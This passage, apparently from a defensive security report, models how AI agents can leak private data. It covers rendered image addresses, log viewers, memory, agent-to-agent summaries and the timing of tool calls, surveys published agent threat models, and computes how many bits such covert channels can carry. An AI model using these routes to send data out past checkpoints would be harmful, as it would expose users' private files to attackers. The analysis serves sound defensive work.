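A checkpoint has to examine traffic in a form that shows what is leaving. Some agents operate a browser through clicks and keystrokes, and a rule based on clicks would do little to identify where data goes. Christodorescu and colleagues describe ceLLMate, a sandbox for such agents that applies its rules to the browser's web requests, which capture the effect of any series of clicks. A proxy that cannot decrypt web traffic can generally read the domain but not the rest of the address, so it could not check for the Heron price.

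Even a well-placed checkpoint never sees requests that start outside the operator's network:

- The user's own browser or phone loads an image or opens a link from home.
- A developer's browser loads an image while displaying a stored conversation in the model provider's log viewer.
- The model provider runs a web search or fetches a page on its own servers.
- A chat app fetches a link to show a preview.
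- A search engine, a remote tool server or another organization's agent makes a further request after receiving a permitted one.

The checkpoint can stop the last kind only by blocking the request that comes before it. For the others, the control has to be in the program that sends the request or in whatever passes the data to that program. Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks* describes a sanitizer of this sort, which stops the client from displaying external images. This removes the graph's edge from the client to the image's server. If another client displays the same reply without the sanitizer, that client's edge remains.

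### The office assistant in the enlarged model

For the assistant with read_mail and search_files, TF001 finds the labels {untrusted, private} and raises no warning. In the enlarged model, the agent's node has the same two labels and passes them to everything that receives its text. For example, the client might keep notes for 30 days, a later session might have the tool post_page, and the second agent might receive a summary every evening.

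Every edge in the table below can carry both untrusted and private data, so the label column omits this and lists only the people who can observe the transfer.

| Component | Edge | Label: observers | Alarm? | Control that removes the alarm |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Model provider | The conversation goes to the provider's servers | The provider's staff | No, if the operator includes them in E | None needed |
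| Chat window | It requests an image | The image server's owner | Yes | Load no outside images |
| Log viewer | It requests an image from a stored reply | The image server's owner | Yes | Display replies as plain text |
| Notes | Saved text goes to later sessions | The user | No, but both labels reach those sessions | None needed on this edge |
| Later session | post_page publishes text | Everyone | Yes | Block posts that depend on untrusted or private notes |
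| Second agent | It publishes text from the summary | Everyone | Yes | Stop sending it summaries |
| User's browser | It opens a link from a reply | The site's owner | Yes | Remove links that the agent wrote |
| User | The user pastes or forwards text | Whoever the user chooses | Yes | None that the operator can fully enforce |

Turning off images changes the result for the chat window, which it does not do under TF001. The alarm for the log viewer remains even if developers agree to review only plain-text copies, because someone can still open the viewer.

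The notes' own edge raises no alarm, but the notes pass both labels to the later session even if the operator disconnects read_mail and search_files before that session starts. The alarm then appears on post_page, where the theft would happen.

The last row prevents a completely clean result. The operator could define the guarantee to end when the user deliberately sends text elsewhere, but would have to disclose this in the scan report. An approval dialog that meets the conditions for consent could support a narrower exception for one transfer.

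Applying one of these controls cannot create a new alarm, because removing an edge or narrowing what can pass along it never adds a label to a node. An operator can therefore deal with the alarms one at a time. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* makes a similar point about explicit security policies, which is that allowing fewer actions never unblocks an action that was already blocked. Adding a component, however, requires a new analysis, because it can connect parts of the graph that were separate.

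A control should remove an alarm only if there is evidence that the control works. Neelou, Malenkovich and Polyakov (2026), in *AI Risk Quadrant for Agent Security*, scored 100 agents and found public evidence for only 17% of the defenses they credited. The other 83% may still work, but an operator who removes an edge because of an unverified claim has no good reason to believe premise 2 still holds. Neelou and colleagues also recommend scoring each agent twice, as the vendor ships it and as the customer has configured it. The chat window should be scored both ways too, because a single setting determines whether it has an edge to the web.

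### What published threat models name

Several published threat models include components that a tool graph leaves out. *Google's Approach for Secure AI Agents* (Díaz, Kern and Olive, 2025) comes closest to the enlarged model. Its diagram of an agent includes the user, memory, tools and rendering, and the paper describes leaks through image addresses and through web addresses that the agent visits. It also warns that malicious text stored in memory can influence later, unrelated tasks. Google does not call the document a threat model, but Shostack + Friends reviews it as one in *Google's approach to AI Agents* and finds the main components there.

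Díaz and colleagues ask developers to record whether an action is read-only or changes something, and whether it handles sensitive data. To assess the risk of data theft, an operator also needs to know who can observe the action, which neither property includes.

MITRE, a US nonprofit research organization, maintains ATLAS, a catalog of attack techniques against AI systems. Its entry for the image attack, *LLM Response Rendering*, correctly identifies the user's client as the program that requests the image, without a click. Its entry for theft through tools, *Exfiltration via AI Agent Tool Invocation*, covers tools "capable of performing write operations", such as sending an email or updating a customer record. A web fetch leaks data as the entry describes, encoded in a tool's inputs, but it writes nothing, so someone who used this definition to assign sink labels would miss fetch_page.

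OWASP, a nonprofit that publishes widely used lists of software security risks, released its list of ten risks for agents in December 2025. The categories in *Agentic Security* (Sotiropoulos, 2026) include poisoned memory, insecure messages between agents, and users who trust an agent too much. None is specifically about a client that loads images. The launch post, *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications* (Sotiropoulos, Katz and Del Rosario, 2025), lists EchoLeak under "Agent Goal Hijack" and the GitHub exploit under supply-chain vulnerabilities.

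Those categories describe how an attack begins, which helps a team prevent injections but is less helpful for finding how data leaves. In Sotiropoulos's example, a variant of EchoLeak, the agent itself sends earlier emails and attachments to an outsider. A reader who learned about the attack from this example might remove the agent's mail tool and leave image loading on. OWASP's 2025 list for language-model applications in general comes closer to covering how data leaves, with a category for output that a developer passes to other software without adequate checks.

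The category for messages between agents covers messages that an attacker forges, alters or replays. In the Heron theft, agent A writes the evening summary itself and sends it to the right recipient, so encryption and authentication would not stop the theft. The category also mentions checking what messages mean. Such a check might catch the price, but only if it takes into account that agent B publishes what it receives.

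Government guidance also treats memory as part of the system. The Australian Cyber Security Centre's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), issued with the US National Security Agency and others, lists the language model, external tools, external data sources, memory and planning workflows as components. It does not list the program that displays the output. Microsoft's *Guarding AI memory* (2026) divides memory protection into storage, retrieval, interaction with the model, and control by the user. According to Microsoft's *Updating the taxonomy of failure modes in agentic AI systems* (2026), the first version of the taxonomy, from April 2025, already included memory poisoning and the impersonation of agents.

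Hashemi Natanzi and Tang (2026), in *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities*, count monitoring components and human operators as part of the system. They argue that a privacy evaluation must state where the data is, because leaks from logs, memories and tool outputs need different defenses. The attack through OpenAI's log viewer supports their argument, since no setting in the bank's application could have stopped it.

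| Component | Where it appears | What the enlarged model adds |
|---|---|---|
| Client | MITRE, Díaz and colleagues | A separate node for each program that displays the text |
| Memory | Díaz and colleagues, Sotiropoulos, Australian Cyber Security Centre, Microsoft | How long each store lasts and which sessions read it |
| User | Díaz and colleagues, Sotiropoulos | Data that the user pastes or forwards |
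| Other agents | Sotiropoulos, Microsoft | Genuine messages that contain private data |
| Logs and monitoring | Hashemi Natanzi and Tang | Requests sent when someone views a log |

An operator could assemble most of the enlarged model's nodes from these documents. The edges are harder to identify because they depend on how a particular system is set up. A general list may include the fact that clients load images, but not that a particular log viewer displays replies from a particular chat application.

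### If nearly every assistant is flagged

The enlarged model would raise an alarm for almost every useful assistant, so people would stop paying attention to it. Neelou and colleagues found that 98 of their 100 agents combined private data, untrusted content and the ability to execute tools. In eight of their ten classes, every agent had all three.

This is not quite the rate at which TF001 would raise an alarm, because a tool that an agent can execute may be unable to send data out. They also chose the agents to represent the market, not at random. Still, the rate gives an idea of how little a single alarm per agent would reveal. If an alarm sounds for 98% of agents, learning whether it sounded for a particular one provides on average only

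−0.98 log₂ 0.98 − 0.02 log₂ 0.02 ≈ 0.14 bits

of information, compared with one bit for an alarm that sounds half the time. Counting clients, memories and users as well would leave even fewer agents without an alarm.

Reporting alarms by edge instead of by agent would help. Nearly every assistant can leak, so an alarm is more useful if it identifies a setting that someone can change, such as one that lets the chat window send text from the Heron file to any web server. Two assistants that both trigger an alarm can also differ greatly in how many edges are responsible and how much each can carry. But almost every report will still include the user's edge and any outside action that the assistant needs for its work.

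A sound threat model would rank edges by what an attacker can observe. An image address that the agent writes can carry whole sentences to a server the attacker chooses, so it ranks highest. A link that the agent selects from a fixed list reveals only which link it selected. A call with no arguments reveals only that the call happened and when. This ranking does not require an estimate of how often the model will follow an injected instruction, a rate that changes with every new model.

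Ranking channels by capacity helps an operator decide what to fix first, but the low-ranked ones still matter because even the narrowest channel can leak a login code or a yes-or-no answer about a takeover. The ranking should therefore compare how much each channel can carry with the length of the secrets that could leak through it.

**Limiting the number of bits.** If an outsider can distinguish at most N different patterns of behavior, they learn at most log₂ N bits. Suppose the assistant may call check_status, the tool without arguments, up to ten times a day. An outsider who learns only the daily total can distinguish 11 values, from zero to ten, which gives

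log₂ 11 ≈ 3.5 bits.

The Heron price, to the nearest million between 1 and 100 million, takes about 6.6 bits to encode. One day's total has only 11 possible values, but two days' totals have 11² = 121 combinations, enough to convey any of the 100 possible prices. A limit on each session or day therefore protects a secret only if the operator also limits how long an attacker can keep collecting.

The limit is much weaker if the outside service logs the time of each call. An eight-hour day has 480 minutes. With at most one call per minute and ten in total, the number of possible patterns is

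C(480, 0) + C(480, 1) + … + C(480, 10) ≈ 2⁶⁷,

where C(480, k) is the number of ways to choose k of the 480 minutes. The same ten calls can then reveal about 67 bits, enough for three six-digit login codes. An operator who counted only the calls would have underestimated the leak by a factor of nearly 20.

A proxy can reduce this leak by delaying calls and sending at most one an hour, at a fixed minute. The outsider then learns at most eight bits over eight hours, because each hour reveals only whether a call was sent. To reduce the leak to zero, the proxy would have to send the request every hour, whether or not the agent asked for it. This works for a status page, because the proxy can save the latest answer until the agent asks for it. It would make no sense for emails or purchases, which should happen only when there is a reason for them.

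An assistant that uses private data to decide which outside actions to take, and when, cannot avoid revealing something about that data through those actions. If the assistant contacts Heron's owners only when the user's files show that the deal is going ahead, the contact itself reveals that it is. Encrypting the message or leaving out the price would not change this. To remove the leak, the assistant would have to do the same thing whatever the files contain, so it could not use them to decide what to do.

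Counting patterns works for a few simple calls but becomes impractical for an agent that browses, writes and runs code. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests estimating an input's effect by removing or changing it and measuring how the agent's actions change. This could show that, in ordinary work, a tool's use rarely depends on a private file. It would not establish a limit on that dependence, because an attacker looks for an instruction that maximizes it.

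**Accepting a stated risk.** For the remaining edges, someone can decide that the benefit is worth the risk and record the decision. An entry for the office assistant might read:

```
Route:       User pastes or forwards the assistant's text
Can carry:   Any text from the user's mail and files
Observers:   Whoever the user chooses
Reason:      The user has to share summaries with colleagues
Accepted by: Head of the deal team
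Review:      March 31, or when a client or tool changes
```

Recording that someone has accepted a route is better than deleting a label to stop the warning, because the next scan still lists the route and shows that it was accepted. The person responsible for the data should make that decision, since an operator who mainly wants the assistant to work has a reason to underestimate the harm.

The task requires the assistant to send Heron's owners the offer price, but a general acceptance would be too broad because it would also let the assistant send them anything else from the file. Security researchers call a controlled release of specified information declassification. Here, the rule could allow the assistant to send only the price, once, to the owners' known address after the user has approved the exact message. The rule cannot prevent the owners from also learning when the buyer was ready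 to make an offer.

An ordinary office assistant can easily do without image loading in the chat window, so the risk of leaks through it should not be accepted. Accepting a risk is easier to justify for a narrow channel that the assistant needs, such as a limited number of calls to a service whose logs outsiders are unlikely to see.
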